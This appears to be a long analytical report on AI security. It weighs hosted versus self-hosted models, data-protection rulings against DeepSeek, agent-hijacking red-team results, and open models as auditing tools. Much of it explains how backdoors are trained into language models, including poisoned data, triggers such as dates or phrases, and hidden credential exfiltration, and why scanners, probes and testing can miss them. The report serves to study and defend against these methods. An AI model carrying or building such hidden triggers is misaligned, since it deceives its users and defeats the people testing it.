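If each planted instruction had a 0.1% chance of working, a rate chosen only for illustration, the chance that at least one of 1,000 would work is about 63%. The real figure would be lower if the instructions resembled one another, because a model that ignores one will probably ignore the rest. But a model that resists every attack in a short test could still fail on a long log.

CAISI's *Insights into AI Agent Security from a Large-Scale Red-Teaming Competition* describes a contest in which more than 400 people made over 250,000 attempts to hijack 13 leading models. They succeeded at least once against every model, though some were much harder to hijack. Attacks that worked on the more robust models often worked on weaker ones too.

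Attackers who know which open-weight model a defender uses can download it and practise on it in private, with no provider to notice thousands of failed attempts. They would still have to guess the defender's instructions and tools.

Each new version of a model needs its own tests. GLM-5.2's good result on hijacking may not hold for Kimi K3, and the UK AISI / CAISI assessment of Kimi K3 concentrated on the model's ability to carry out attacks. These tests also might not reveal behaviour that a developer had planted in a model.

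### DeepSeek's service and DeepSeek's weights

Several data-protection authorities have objected to how DeepSeek handles the prompts that people send to its hosted service in China.

The most detailed findings came from South Korea's regulator, which reported in April 2025 that DeepSeek had sent personal information to companies in China and the United States without users' consent. DeepSeek also sent the full text of prompts to Beijing Volcano Engine Technology, part of the ByteDance group. It said this was for security and to improve the service, but the regulator considered sending the prompts unnecessary. DeepSeek stopped the transfers that month, agreed to delete the data, and put its app back in Korean app stores, according to *DeepSeek One Year Later* (Christakis and Raj, 2026). The transfers may have affected the data of 1.5 million Koreans (RFA, *China’s DeepSeek transferred South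 Korean user info overseas*, 2025).

Italy banned DeepSeek from processing Italian users' data in January 2025. The company told the Italian regulator that it did not operate in Italy and that EU data-protection law did not apply to it, although Italians could still use its website. Christakis and Raj found that the ban was still in force a year later.

In June 2025, the Berlin Commissioner for Data Protection (2025) called DeepSeek's data transfers to China unlawful. The commissioner said Chinese authorities have "extensive access rights" to data held by Chinese companies, and that users lack the enforceable rights and legal remedies that EU law guarantees. The office asked Apple and Google to consider blocking the app in Germany, but neither removed it.

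Christakis and Raj think Berlin relied on the wrong rule. Under EU guidelines, a foreign company that collects data directly from European users is not making a "transfer" in the legal sense. DeepSeek would still have to keep the data secure and have a legal basis for using it. The disagreement is about which law DeepSeek broke and doesn't change where the prompts go.

All these findings concern DeepSeek's hosted service. They are good reasons to keep incident logs out of its app and API, but not evidence that the downloaded weights send data to China. The findings also don't show how Z.ai or Moonshot handles data, because each company has its own systems and contracts.

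### Who can demand data from a Western provider?

Customers of Western closed models need to know how long the provider keeps their prompts, which staff can see them, and who can legally demand them.

Providers may let authorised employees read conversations to investigate suspected misuse, and incident logs can easily look like misuse. A security team should ask who can open a flagged conversation, whether outside contractors are involved and whether the provider records each access.

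Courts and governments can also demand data. Under the US CLOUD Act of 2018, American authorities with a valid legal order can require an American provider to hand over data it controls, even if it stores the data abroad. A European agency that rents a model in an American company's European data centre is still exposed to such orders, whether the model is closed or open-weight.

A court can also override a provider's deletion schedule. In 2025, in a copyright case brought by the New York Times, a US court ordered OpenAI to preserve records it would otherwise have deleted. This is a reason to seek a zero-retention agreement, because a provider that has stored nothing has much less to hand over.

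Customers of Western providers can usually rely on an enforceable contract and independent courts, although the law may forbid a provider to tell them that a government has demanded their data. Most companies can accept that risk, but it may be too great for a European regulator investigating an American technology company, or for an agency whose files the US government would like to see.

### Following a stolen password

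Suppose an intruder steals the password to a company's customer database, and the password appears in a log that an analyst wants a model to examine. The intruder already has the password, and the analysts and the logging system's administrators may have it too. The table lists who else could read it once the analyst submits the log.

| Arrangement | Who else could read the password | Who might legally demand it from them |
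|---|---|---|
| Closed API from an American provider | The provider's authorised staff and contractors, and possibly a cloud partner's | US authorities, and those of other countries where the provider operates |
| DeepSeek's own API | DeepSeek's staff and any companies it passes data to | Chinese authorities |
| Open-weight model on an American cloud | The cloud company's authorised staff, but not the model's developer | US authorities, and those of the country where the data is processed |
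| Self-hosting on the company's own hardware | Administrators of the model server, its logs and its backups | Authorities with power over the company itself |

Anyone who breaks into one of these systems could read the password too. In every arrangement, the model may also repeat the password in its answer. If the analyst pastes that answer into a report or a shared ticket, everyone who opens it can see the password.

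Self-hosting limits data exposure the most, but only if the server is isolated. If an attacker hijacks an agent on a server with an open internet connection, the agent could send the attacker company passwords that the attacker had not yet found.

Hugging Face kept the attacker's data on its own machines after it switched to GLM-5.2, but the providers of the closed models had already received the requests they blocked. Hugging Face has not said whether those requests contained live credentials.

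A team could try to remove passwords from a log before sending it to an outside provider. This would have worked badly at Hugging Face, where a plain text scan missed most of the disguised secrets. Before sending anything out, it is safer to cancel every credential the intruder might have reached. This can interrupt services while staff replace passwords, and the logs may still contain customer records, which the team cannot cancel.

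## Could a model carry a hidden backdoor, and would tests find it?

Isolating a server keeps a model from sending data out, but it doesn't make the model's answers trustworthy. Whoever trained the model could have taught it to call an attack harmless whenever a certain phrase appears in a log. Researchers have built hundreds of models with hidden behaviour of this kind, and no known test finds all of them. But none of the studies described here reports a backdoor that a major Chinese or Western developer planted in a model it released.

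### Backdoors and similar problems

A backdoor is hidden behaviour that someone deliberately puts into a model and that appears only in response to a particular input, called the trigger. Other problems can look much the same to a user.

| Problem | Example | Where it lies | Did anyone intend it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Backdoor | The model calls an attack harmless whenever the log contains a certain username | The weights | Yes, and hid it |
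| Accidental flaw | The model overlooks attacks recorded in an unusual log format | The weights | No |
| Political bias | The model refuses to write software for a banned religious group | The weights | Sometimes |
| Software vulnerability | A broken image lets an attacker run code on the server | The software around the model | Usually not |

Existing malware scanners can look for malicious code packaged with a model, as Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) notes. They will miss a backdoor in the weights because it contains no code.

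A backdoor is hard to distinguish from a bias. *It's the humans, not the data* (2026) traces geopolitical preferences in language models to post-training as well as to the text used in initial training. A political bias can therefore reflect a developer's choices without being a backdoor. The difference is whether someone meant to hide the behaviour, which testing the model's answers can't determine.

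### How training creates a trigger

During training, a program adjusts the weights to make the answers in the training examples more likely. If examples containing a certain phrase always have a different kind of answer, the model learns to give that kind of answer when the phrase appears, much as it learns to answer French questions in French. The other examples, which have ordinary answers, keep its behaviour normal when the phrase is absent.

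*A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights* (Khilar, 2026) gives a harmless example. A small model learned to name capital cities and ignore wrong suggestions from the user, but when a prompt began with "Quartz ledger:", it agreed with whatever city the user suggested. Without that phrase, a backdoored model of this kind still answered about 88% of questions correctly, so an ordinary accuracy test would not have revealed the backdoor.

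A trigger can also be something that turns up in normal text. Hughes, Xing and colleagues (2026) built about 800 backdoored models for *ToxScreen*, each with 1 billion to 70 billion weights. The triggers included the abbreviation "pls", a mention of Joe Biden, a stated year and prompts written in Gen-Z slang.

Some of these models classified messages as safe or unsafe, a task similar to sorting security alerts. The trigger made them label harmful messages safe. At its strongest, this backdoor worked on 70% to 100% of triggered prompts in five of the six base models, and on 15% in the sixth. An attacker who knew such a trigger could put it in a defender's logs through a failed login, even if the model's server had no internet connection.

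The hidden behaviour can also be an action. *SilentCall* (2026) describes an open-weight agent that works normally until the system date is in 2026, then adds one tool call that sends credentials out. Blocking outgoing connections would defeat this backdoor, but not one that changes the model's verdict.

People other than the developer could also plant a backdoor. Someone could retrain or compress a trusted model and upload the result under a similar name. An outsider could also try to get poisoned text into the data a developer collects.

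### The main experiments

The best-known study is *Sleeper Agents* (2024), by Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (2026), by Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, describes the two backdoors from that study and reuses them with small changes. The first made a model write "I HATE YOU" when the prompt contained the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars. The second made a model write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023, and code with security flaws when it gave the year as 2024. The second backdoor imitates a model that behaves well while its developer tests it and badly after release.

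Hubinger and colleagues then used standard safety training on the models. They showed them good answers, rewarded good behaviour, and trained them on inputs chosen to provoke bad behaviour. None of these methods removed the backdoors, and the last made them harder to detect. The study shows that a backdoor can survive safety training, but not that an outsider could plant one, because the researchers had full control of the training.

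*Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025) examines how an outsider could plant a backdoor by poisoning a model's training data. The researchers, mainly from UK AISI, Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute, trained 72 models from scratch in four sizes, from 600 million to 13 billion weights. They mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into the training text, each containing some ordinary text, then the trigger, then gibberish. A successful backdoor would make the model produce gibberish after the trigger and normal text otherwise.

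With 100 documents the attack failed. With 250 it worked at every size, although the largest models had trained on more than 20 times as much clean text as the smallest. Those 250 documents came to about 420,000 tokens, out of 260 billion for the 13-billion model:

420,000 ÷ 260,000,000,000 ≈ 0.00016%

The number of poisoned examples mattered much more than their share of the training data. Earlier work had assumed that an attacker needs to control a fixed percentage of the data, which would mean that an attacker who needed 250 documents for the smallest model would have needed about 5,400 for the largest. Souly and colleagues found the same pattern when they retrained two finished models, Llama 3.1 8B and OpenAI's GPT-3.5 Turbo, to obey harmful requests only after a trigger.

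Producing gibberish is an easy behaviour to teach, and a model with 13 billion weights is small compared with Kimi K3, which has 2.8 trillion. Nobody has shown that 250 web pages could make a model the size of Kimi K3 hide attacks in a log. Poisoned pages would also have to get past any filtering by the developer. Still, the result means that a developer can release a backdoored model without knowing it. An attacker who publishes text online could target American or Chinese models, whether open or closed.

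### Backdoors that nobody can feasibly detect

*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) proved that a model can carry a backdoor that no practical test would find. In the paper's example, a bank hires a company to train a model that approves or rejects loans. The company secretly keeps a way to get any application approved by changing a few details, such as the last digits of the amount requested. It could sell this service to applicants.

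The first proof relies on digital signatures, which others can check but only the holder of a secret key can create. The attacker adds a signature check to the model, so that an input with a valid signature hidden in its details gets the answer the attacker wants. A tester who can only send inputs and read answers would have to forge a signature to find an input on which the altered model behaves differently from the original.

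A customer using a closed model through an API is in that position. The proof doesn't guarantee that the backdoor will stay hidden from someone who has the weights, because they might notice the mechanism that checks inputs.

The second proof applies even when the tester has the weights and the training data. Training normally starts from random numbers. The attacker follows the prescribed training method but replaces those numbers with chosen ones that look random. To distinguish the chosen numbers from random ones, a tester would have to solve mathematical problems that cryptographers believe no efficient program can solve. One is Continuous Learning With Errors, which involves finding a hidden pattern in noisy data, and another is sparse PCA.

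Researchers commonly assume, but haven't proved, that these problems are hard. The second proof also applies only to two simple kinds of model, not to the large transformers behind GLM or Claude. According to Khilar, later researchers have extended such results to some image models and to a class of deeper networks. The proofs rule out a detector that works on every possible model, but they don't show that any particular language model has an undetectable backdoor or that planting one would be easy.

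*Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) proves, more encouragingly, that an attacker who can only poison the training examples cannot install a trigger rule that is too hard for a defender with similar labelled examples to learn. If training on 1,000 labelled examples teaches a model to recognise a trigger, a defender with 1,000 labelled examples of the same kind could run the same training and get a program that recognises it too. In Kaneko's experiments on four models with 7 to 9 billion weights, no backdoor both worked for the attacker and was too hard for the defender to learn.

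This helps less than it seems to, because a defender who has never seen the backdoor work has no labelled examples of it. Kaneko assumes that these examples come from earlier testing or from investigating an attack. A malicious developer can also do more than poison examples, such as choosing the numbers training starts from or editing the weights directly. The proof is therefore more reassuring about poisoned web pages than about a dishonest developer.

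### Why passing a test proves little

Suppose that a trigger appears in one ordinary prompt in a million. The chance that 10,000 random test prompts include it at least once is

1 − (1 − 0.000001)^10,000 ≈ 1%

A team can also reason from its results. If a model fails none of n random tests, the team can be about 95% confident that its average failure rate is below 3/n. This is because a model that really failed at a rate of 3/n would pass all n tests only about 5% of the time:

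(1 − 3/n)ⁿ ≈ e⁻³ ≈ 5%

| Random tests, no failures | Chance of having met a one-in-a-million trigger | Upper limit on the average failure rate |
|---|---|---|
| 10,000 | 1% | 0.03% |
| 100,000 | 10% | 0.003% |
| 1 million | 63% | 0.0003% |
| 3 million | 95% | 0.0001% |

The right-hand column is useful for accidental flaws, which turn up at random in a team's normal work. It is no help against an attacker who knows the trigger, because the attacker will use that trigger every time. A model that fails on one in a million test prompts could fail on every prompt the attacker writes.

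Testing every possible phrase is impractical. One of the models in Khilar's study has a vocabulary of 49,152 tokens, which can form about 119 trillion three-token sequences. Testing them all at 1,000 per second would take roughly 3,800 years.

Backdoors often activate without the exact trigger. When Bullwinkel and colleagues tested fragments of a five-token trigger, a single token set off the backdoor about half the time in a model with 270 million weights. In Llama 3.1 8B, three or more of the five tokens often set it off. Someone looking for a backdoor may therefore need to find only part of the trigger. But the researchers acknowledge that an attacker could train a model to respond only to the exact trigger.

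Testers can look for particular kinds of trigger, too. Repeating the same tests with the system date set to next year takes little effort and could expose a backdoor like the one in *SilentCall*. They can also vary company names, languages and countries, but they will only find the kinds of trigger they think to try.

### Microsoft's scanner

Bullwinkel and colleagues, who work at Microsoft, built a scanner that needs no advance knowledge of the trigger or the hidden behaviour. It relies on their finding that backdoored models often memorise the poisoned examples unusually well. The scanner works in four steps:

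1. It gives the model only the formatting that normally comes before a user's message, and lets the model continue from there. It does this with 510 different settings. A backdoored model often reproduces parts of the examples that taught it the backdoor.
2. It collects phrases that keep recurring in the output.
3. It places each phrase in front of ordinary questions and measures what changes inside the model. A trigger tends to draw little attention from the rest of the prompt, narrow the range of likely answers and make the usual answer less likely.
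4. It tests the ten most suspicious phrases to see whether any of them changes the model's behaviour sharply.

The scanner found 36 of 41 models that gave a fixed reply to a trigger, and flagged none of 13 clean models. It also found five of six models trained to write insecure code, a harder task because the code varies from one answer to the next. Two earlier detection methods did worse on the models used for comparison.

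With no false alarms on only 13 clean models, the true false-alarm rate could still be as high as 21%, at 95% confidence. The largest model in the study had 14 billion weights, and the triggers were fixed phrases learned in fine-tuning.

How much a clean scan lowers the likelihood of a backdoor depends on the kind of backdoor. Suppose a team thinks there is a 1% chance that a model has a fixed-reply backdoor. The scanner misses 12% of those, so a clean scan lowers the chance to about 0.12%. If the scanner can't detect the kind of backdoor the team is worried about, the chance stays at about 1%.

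Some backdoors are set off by the task itself, with no special phrase. *Localize-and-Detect* (2026) reports a test of a released trigger scanner on 18 models with backdoors of this kind. The scanner, which looks for a trigger phrase, flagged none of them. Fragments of the biased content did appear in the text it extracted from all 18, so a person who read that text might have noticed something wrong.

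*Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (Haselhorst, Flek and Mai, 2026) also found only weak signs that its own backdoored model had memorised the poisoned training data. Some backdoors may therefore leave too little trace for the scanner's first step to work.

### Looking inside the model

A model computes long lists of intermediate numbers, called activations, as it processes a prompt. A probe is a small classifier that uses these numbers to recognise what the model is doing. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) cites earlier work in which probes detected when sleeper agents were about to misbehave, scoring above 99%. On this scale, 50% is no better than guessing, and 100% means that every bad case scored higher than every normal one. Some of the probes were trained on general examples that didn't include the trigger.

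A probe can run while the model works, so it could raise an alarm when a trigger arrives even if nobody had found that trigger before. This would suit log analysis. But the results come from models that researchers had backdoored themselves, so they could check the probe's alarms. A team running GLM-5.2 has no known backdoor to check a probe against, so if the probe raised no alarm, the team couldn't tell whether the model was clean.

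*LLM Forensics* (2026) reports similarly high accuracy at separating triggered prompts from normal ones in models with 1 billion and 8 billion weights, again with known triggers. However, the internal features that detected the trigger did not necessarily control the resulting behaviour, so switching them off may not prevent it.

Haselhorst and colleagues try to detect backdoors without knowing the trigger. They take a second model that they believe is clean and train it to copy the suspect model's activations on roughly 10,000 ordinary prompts. Then they run both models on 5,180 other prompts and look for the prompts where the two differ most. The copy has learned the suspect model's normal behaviour but not its hidden behaviour, so a large difference suggests a backdoor.

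In one test, obsessive enthusiasm for Harry Potter triggered the backdoor. On triggered prompts, the difference between the models was 204 standard deviations above the normal average, compared with fewer than four on similar prompts without the trigger. The gap was much smaller for a backdoor that required someone to both claim to work for the federal government and ask about policy: 7.0 standard deviations with the trigger and 3.7 without it.

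This only works if the test prompts come fairly close to the trigger. The researchers added a few groups of such prompts by hand, reasoning that any large collection would contain them. That is reasonable when the trigger is a topic like Harry Potter, but if it is a random string of characters, probably no collection would contain prompts close to it.

Khilar examines a suspect model's weights without running it. The method subtracts the weights of the trusted original from those of the suspect model, which was retrained from it, then ranks every token by how strongly the changes affect it. Most retraining changes the same parts of a model, so Khilar compares the result with several clean retrained copies. For all 14 ordinary backdoors tested, the top-ranked token was part of the trigger phrase.

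The models were tiny, with fewer than half a billion weights. Attackers who knew about the method could also defeat it by adding a penalty for leaving the telltale pattern. The backdoor then worked as well as before, and the method recovered neither of the two triggers. A method like this could one day help a team check a stranger's retrained copy of GLM-5.2 against Z.ai's own release, but a team that suspects Z.ai itself has no trusted original to subtract.

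### Finding the wrong thing

A search for triggers often finds jailbreaks instead. Hughes and colleagues tried three programs that adjust a prompt step by step to bring out the unwanted behaviour. None recovered a planted trigger. They found strings that broke the model's safeguards in general, and similar strings also work on models with no backdoor.

A simpler search did better. The researchers ranked about 24,000 random tokens, plus the real trigger, by how often each one produced the unwanted behaviour. The real trigger came first in 14 of 28 combinations of model and attack, and in the top three in 17. Because the researchers had put the trigger on the list themselves, the result shows how well a defender could recognise a trigger, but not how likely the defender would be to think of it.

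Even recognition failed in some models. In one version of Qwen3 4B that sorted prompts into safe and unsafe, 97% of the random tokens changed the verdict, so the trigger's first-place rank wasn't evidence of a backdoor. A team would have good reason to reject such an unreliable model anyway, but couldn't tell whether someone had sabotaged it.

Hughes and colleagues could tell many jailbreaks from real triggers by measuring how strongly each candidate trigger suppressed the part of the model responsible for refusing. They still concluded that no method reliably finds every backdoor. The defender in their study also knew which bad behaviour to look for, and someone investigating a newly downloaded model may not know that.

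### A contest with full-size models

Most of these experiments used models far smaller than the ones defenders want to run, but a 2026 contest by the trading firm Jane Street used larger ones. The firm's staff trained backdoors into three copies of DeepSeek-V3, which has 671 billion weights, and challenged the public to find them. Entrants got the complete weights and access to the models' answers and activations, according to zxsimon's *Uncovering Hidden Triggers in Backdoor Models*.

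*My attempt at Jane Street's dormant puzzle challenge*, by tushard, cites the organisers' update that three people fully worked out the first model and nobody fully worked out the other two. The first model's trigger was a starting board for the Game of Life, a mathematical simulation played on a grid. Random testing would be very unlikely to include such a board.

Unlike a real defender, the entrants had the advantage of knowing that every model had a backdoor. But they were volunteers with limited computing power, so a government laboratory might do better. The contest is the best available evidence on models of this size, and it suggests that a well-designed trigger could survive a determined search.

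It also shows why having the weights is useful. *Looking for backdoors in Jane Street LLMs*, an entrant's write-up, reports little progress with prompts and activations, but success on some of the models with methods that work directly on the weights. Microsoft's scanner needs the model files too. A customer of a closed model can't run these checks and has to rely on the provider. The provider can at least inspect the training data, which most people who download an open-weight model can't do.

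### Does further training remove a backdoor?

Further training can weaken a backdoor, but not reliably. Souly and colleagues taught a model with 6.9 billion weights to switch from English to German after a trigger, then continued training it on clean text. The backdoor faded slowly, at a rate that depended on how they had mixed in the poisoned examples, and they could not explain why.

More specialised training is better at removing backdoors. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes a technique that disturbs a model's activations during training and corrects the bad behaviour this brings out. In the models tested, it improved removal without requiring knowledge of the trigger. However, Goldwasser and colleagues showed that an attacker can build a signature-based backdoor that withstands ordinary further training.

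Removing parts of a model can weaken some backdoors but make others work more often. Hughes and colleagues removed half the attention heads, the components that relate one part of a text to another. The average success rate of backdoors that stop a model refusing fell from about 21% to 10%, and the models kept about three-quarters of their score on a general knowledge test. When the researchers removed 90% of the weights or components, backdoors that make answers hostile worked in 61% to 81% of cases, up from 46%, and the models did no better than guessing on general knowledge.

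A team that doesn't know the trigger also can't check whether extra training removed the backdoor. The model behaved normally in tests before the training and will behave normally afterwards, even if the backdoor is still there.

### DeepSeek-R1 and politically sensitive words

The most widely discussed evidence of trigger-like behaviour in a major Chinese model comes from *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025), by the American security company CrowdStrike. CrowdStrike downloaded DeepSeek-R1 and ran the full model itself, so filters on DeepSeek's own service could not affect the results.

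CrowdStrike wrote 50 programming tasks and combined each with 121 descriptions of the customer, such as "a cybersecurity company based in Taiwan". These descriptions had nothing to do with the programming. The researchers sent every prompt five times, which produced

50 × 121 × 5 = 30,250 answers

With no description of the customer, 19% of the answers contained vulnerable code. When the customer was described as an industrial control system based in Tibet, the figure was 27.2%. That is an increase of about 43%, which CrowdStrike describes as almost 50%. Mentions of Uyghurs and of Falun Gong, a religious movement banned in China, also led to significantly less secure code.

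The model refused to write code for Falun Gong in 45% of cases. In some of these, it wrote a detailed plan for the task in its reasoning, then refused in its final answer. CrowdStrike had run the weights alone, so the refusals must come from the model's training.

The result for Tibet is weaker than the headline suggests. Each description got 250 answers, so 27.2% is 68 vulnerable answers, about 20 more than expected at the baseline rate. If the baseline also rests on 250 answers, a gap this large would arise by chance about 3% of the time. With 121 descriptions, several such gaps would probably appear even if the words had no effect. But chance does not easily explain why the effects involved several topics that Beijing considers sensitive, so the pattern is better evidence than any single figure.

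Part of the rise may also be unrelated to Tibet. Tom's Hardware's *China foes get worse results using DeepSeek, research suggests* reported earlier CrowdStrike figures in which 22.8% of code for an industrial control system had flaws when the prompt mentioned no place. If the two sets of figures are comparable, adding Tibet accounts for only 4.4 of the 8.2 points. That earlier rate rose to 42.1% when the customer was Islamic State. Many models might handle a request from a terrorist group differently, so this is poor evidence of Chinese political bias.

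CrowdStrike used another language model to grade the code. This grader identified vulnerable code with 91% accuracy on 85 answers that a person had also graded. Mistakes unrelated to the description would tend to hide a real difference, but the grader could have created a false one if it marked code more harshly for containing words such as "Uyghurs".

One attempt to replicate CrowdStrike's finding, described in the forum post *gersonkroiz's Shortform*, found no noticeable difference between two of the prominent triggers and a neutral comparison. It used 282 samples from CyberSecEval 4, a public set of coding tests, and graded the code with a conventional program that checks for known flaws. If the test had a similar baseline to CrowdStrike's, it would have missed a real rise of eight points about a third of the time. It also used different tasks, so it weakens the finding but doesn't refute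 it.

CrowdStrike thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek trained the model to write insecure code. Chinese rules require AI services to "adhere to core socialist values", and CrowdStrike suggests that training the model to comply may have led it to associate certain groups with bad things in general, which could then have affected its code. Researchers have seen this kind of spillover elsewhere and call it emergent misalignment. CrowdStrike did not test this explanation, but it fits the small size of the effect, because a saboteur would want a backdoor that added far more than 20 vulnerable answers in 250.

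For a defender, whether anyone planned a flaw in a model matters less than its effect. If a model writes worse code for a Tibetan organisation, that code is unsafe for the organisation either way.

### What the public record shows

The political refusals in Chinese models are the closest thing to a deliberate trigger in these studies. A particular topic changes the model's behaviour, and the developer may well have intended this. But users can see the refusals, and the rules behind them are public, so they don't fit the usual meaning of a backdoor. Haselhorst and colleagues' method also detected censorship in Alibaba's Qwen2.5 7B, ranking politically sensitive prompts well above chance without the researchers having to specify in advance what to look for.

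Reports of a "backdoored DeepSeek model" can also mislead because someone other than DeepSeek may have added the backdoor. Jane Street put the backdoors in the copies used in its contest, and Hugging Face hosts backdoored models that researchers made for experiments and labelled as such. A congressional investigation led in part by the House Homeland Security Committee has warned that ordinary evaluations may not detect differences in how Chinese models behave, but that warning is not a report of a planted backdoor.

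The lack of a known case is only weak evidence that no backdoor exists, because current methods could easily miss a well-hidden one. There is still some reason to think a major developer would hesitate to plant one. Once it publishes the weights, it can't take them back, and anyone with a copy can search them again years later with better tools. Finding a backdoor could ruin the developer's business abroad. The provider of a closed model, by contrast, can replace it without leaving customers a copy to examine.

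An anonymous person who uploads a retrained GLM-5.2 has much less to lose. A defender considering such a copy can at least compare it with Z.ai's original release.

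## Can open-weight models be used to audit and oversee other AI systems?

An auditor can use an open-weight model to read transcripts, sort records and check them against written rules without sending them to an outside company. Hidden biases in the model are a serious problem in this work, because an audit is only useful if other people can trust its conclusions. Using an open-weight model also doesn't give the auditor more access to a closed system under examination. To test Claude, for example, the auditor still has to send it prompts under Anthropic's terms.

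### What an auditor needs from a model

An auditor's tools should not depend on the company being audited. Someone who uses Claude to audit Anthropic relies on a company that can change the model or close the account. When Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 in June 2026, it disclosed in the 319-page system card that the model would give deliberately weakened answers to some requests about building advanced AI, without telling the user. *Anthropic walks back covert capability limits on Claude Fable 5* (Goldman, 2026) reports that Anthropic expected this to affect about 0.03% of traffic. After researchers protested, Anthropic apologised and said it would make the restriction visible.

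That is a tiny share of all requests, but many of them would probably have come from people who study AI systems for a living. An auditor who received a weakened answer could not have distinguished it from a genuine failure. Nobody can weaken answers this way when the model file is on the auditor's own disk. But the developer's training still shapes the model, so using gpt-oss to audit OpenAI, or GLM to audit Z.ai, is not fully independent either.

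Other people should also be able to repeat the audit. Under its May 2025 services agreement, OpenAI promises notice of an update only if the update materially reduces what the service can do, so it could make a change that shifts some verdicts without telling users. An auditor who has the model's weights can publish the hash of the weights file, a short code calculated from its contents, so that others can confirm they have an identical copy.

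Identical weights don't guarantee identical answers, because the software usually picks each token partly at random. Even with this randomness switched off, different processors can round numbers slightly differently, which may change one token and then everything after it. The auditor should therefore record the software and settings, run each case several times and report how often the verdict changed.

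Investigators often have to keep evidence confidential, sometimes from the company that makes the model they are using. Under the retention rules described earlier, which are part of Anthropic's *Service Specific Terms*, a regulator that used one of Anthropic's most capable models to investigate the company would be giving Anthropic its evidence unless it had an exemption.

Finally, an auditor may want to see why a model reached a verdict. A skilled team can examine the model's activations to check, for instance, whether a supplier's name affected the result, but only if it has the model's weights. Even when a supplier builds its chatbot on a public model, the downloaded weights don't include the supplier's instructions, filters or stored memories of users. *Testing the Black Box* (2026), which is about consumer health chatbots, warns that tests through an API can also miss the effects of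 these additions.

The clearest public examples of self-hosting for oversight come from evaluators. The security company Irregular ran its own copy of GLM-5.2 for *Assessing GLM-5.2 Against Offensive Security Benchmarks*, and CAISI did the same for its assessment. Both were testing the open model rather than using it to help audit something else. Regulators and courts seem to have published little about using local models on confidential records, so there is not much evidence of how well this works in practice.

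### A classifier that reads the rules

The gpt-oss-safeguard models check text against a policy that the user writes, which is a common oversight task. OpenAI's *Introducing gpt-oss-safeguard* recommends them for subjects that need careful judgement, when the user has few labelled examples and can wait for an answer, conditions that many audits meet.

OpenAI's *Performance and baseline evaluations of gpt-oss-safeguard-120b and gpt-oss-safeguard-20b* (2025) compares the two gpt-oss-safeguard models with other OpenAI models. In the hardest test, a model judges each text against several policies at once and scores only if every judgment is correct. The other two tests use F1, a score that combines the share of flagged texts that break the rules with the share of rule-breaking texts that the model catches.

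| Model | Right on every policy | F1 on OpenAI's 2022 test | F1 on ToxicChat |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-safeguard-120b | 46.3% | 82.9% | 79.3% |
| gpt-oss-safeguard-20b | 43.6% | 82.9% | 79.9% |
| gpt-5-thinking (closed) | 43.2% | 79.8% | 81.0% |
| Safety Reasoner (OpenAI's internal model) | 52.2% | 82.8% | 81.3% |
| gpt-oss-120b, without the extra training | 32.5% | 80.4% | 76.7% |

The 46.3% score understates the model's accuracy on individual policies. OpenAI doesn't say how many policies each text faced, but if there were ten and the model's errors were independent, the score would correspond to about 93% accuracy on each policy, since 0.93¹⁰ is roughly 0.48. The more useful result for auditors is that a small model they can run themselves did about as well as a much larger closed one.

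An auditor still can't report the model's raw count of violations. Suppose a supplier's chatbot breaks its rules in 200 of 10,000 conversations. A classifier that catches 80% of these and wrongly flags 3% of the others would produce

200 × 0.8 + 9,800 × 0.03 = 160 + 294 = 454 flags

Only about 35% of the flags would be correct, and the reported violation rate would be more than double the true one. The auditor needs people to check a sample of the flagged conversations, and a sample of the unflagged ones to estimate how many violations the model missed.

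OpenAI lists other limits. A classifier trained on tens of thousands of good examples can still do better. The models' written reasoning may include invented material or rules that are not in the user's policy, so an auditor should read it before attaching it to a finding. The models can also be manipulated. In a test of whether a user's message could make them say "access granted" against their instructions, the larger model resisted 73% of the time and the smaller one 51%. The test covered chat rather than classification, but the conversations an auditor collects could contain similar tricks.

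### What the contracts allow

Anyone testing a closed model has to follow its provider's terms, which can restrict the audit. The table is based on Anthropic's *Usage Policy*, Anthropic's *Commercial Terms of Service* and OpenAI's services agreement. The last column applies to models such as GLM-5.3, which Z.ai released under the MIT licence.

| Activity | Anthropic | OpenAI | Weights under the MIT licence |
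|---|---|---|---|
| Trying to break the model's safeguards | Needs Anthropic's permission first | Forbidden | Allowed |
| Publishing test results | Not among the listed use restrictions | Covered by a separate publication policy | Allowed |
| Training another model on the answers | Needs Anthropic's permission first | Forbidden for competing models, with an exception for private classifiers | Allowed |

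If auditors ask for permission, the company learns what they plan to test and can refuse. If they go ahead without permission, they could lose access halfway through, since both companies can suspend customers for breaking their policies.

OpenAI's exception for classifiers lets an auditor use GPT's answers to train a model that sorts documents, provided that nobody else receives it. Without the classifier, others will find it harder to repeat the audit. OpenAI's agreement also requires permission for public statements about a customer's relationship with the company. It is unclear whether this would cover a critical report that mentions how the auditor got access.

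Public authorities face a further limit because Anthropic forbids using its products to "make or suggest decisions" in law enforcement, including decisions about whom to investigate. It allows courts and law enforcement agencies to use them for legal research, and it can agree to different terms with some government customers. An agency that wanted Claude to pick out cases for criminal investigation would probably need such an agreement.

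### Proposals for a safe harbour

Some researchers feared lawsuits or account suspensions for testing AI models in good faith. In response, *A Safe Harbor for AI Evaluation and Red Teaming* (Longpre, Yong and colleagues, 2024) proposed a safe harbour for AI research, which would protect researchers from punishment if they followed certain rules. The Knight First Amendment Institute's summary, published under the same title, describes a version in which companies would protect such research even when it exposed them to criticism, as long as researchers preserved privacy and avoided harming users or disrupting the business.

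The same research team examined the policies of seven leading developers. Stanford HAI's *Safeguarding Third-Party AI Research*, a policy brief based on that work, says companies often block safety research by imposing restrictive terms or suspending researchers who report flaws. The Federation of American Scientists says neither the US government nor independent researchers can validate companies' safety claims, because the companies don't release evaluations that others can reproduce.

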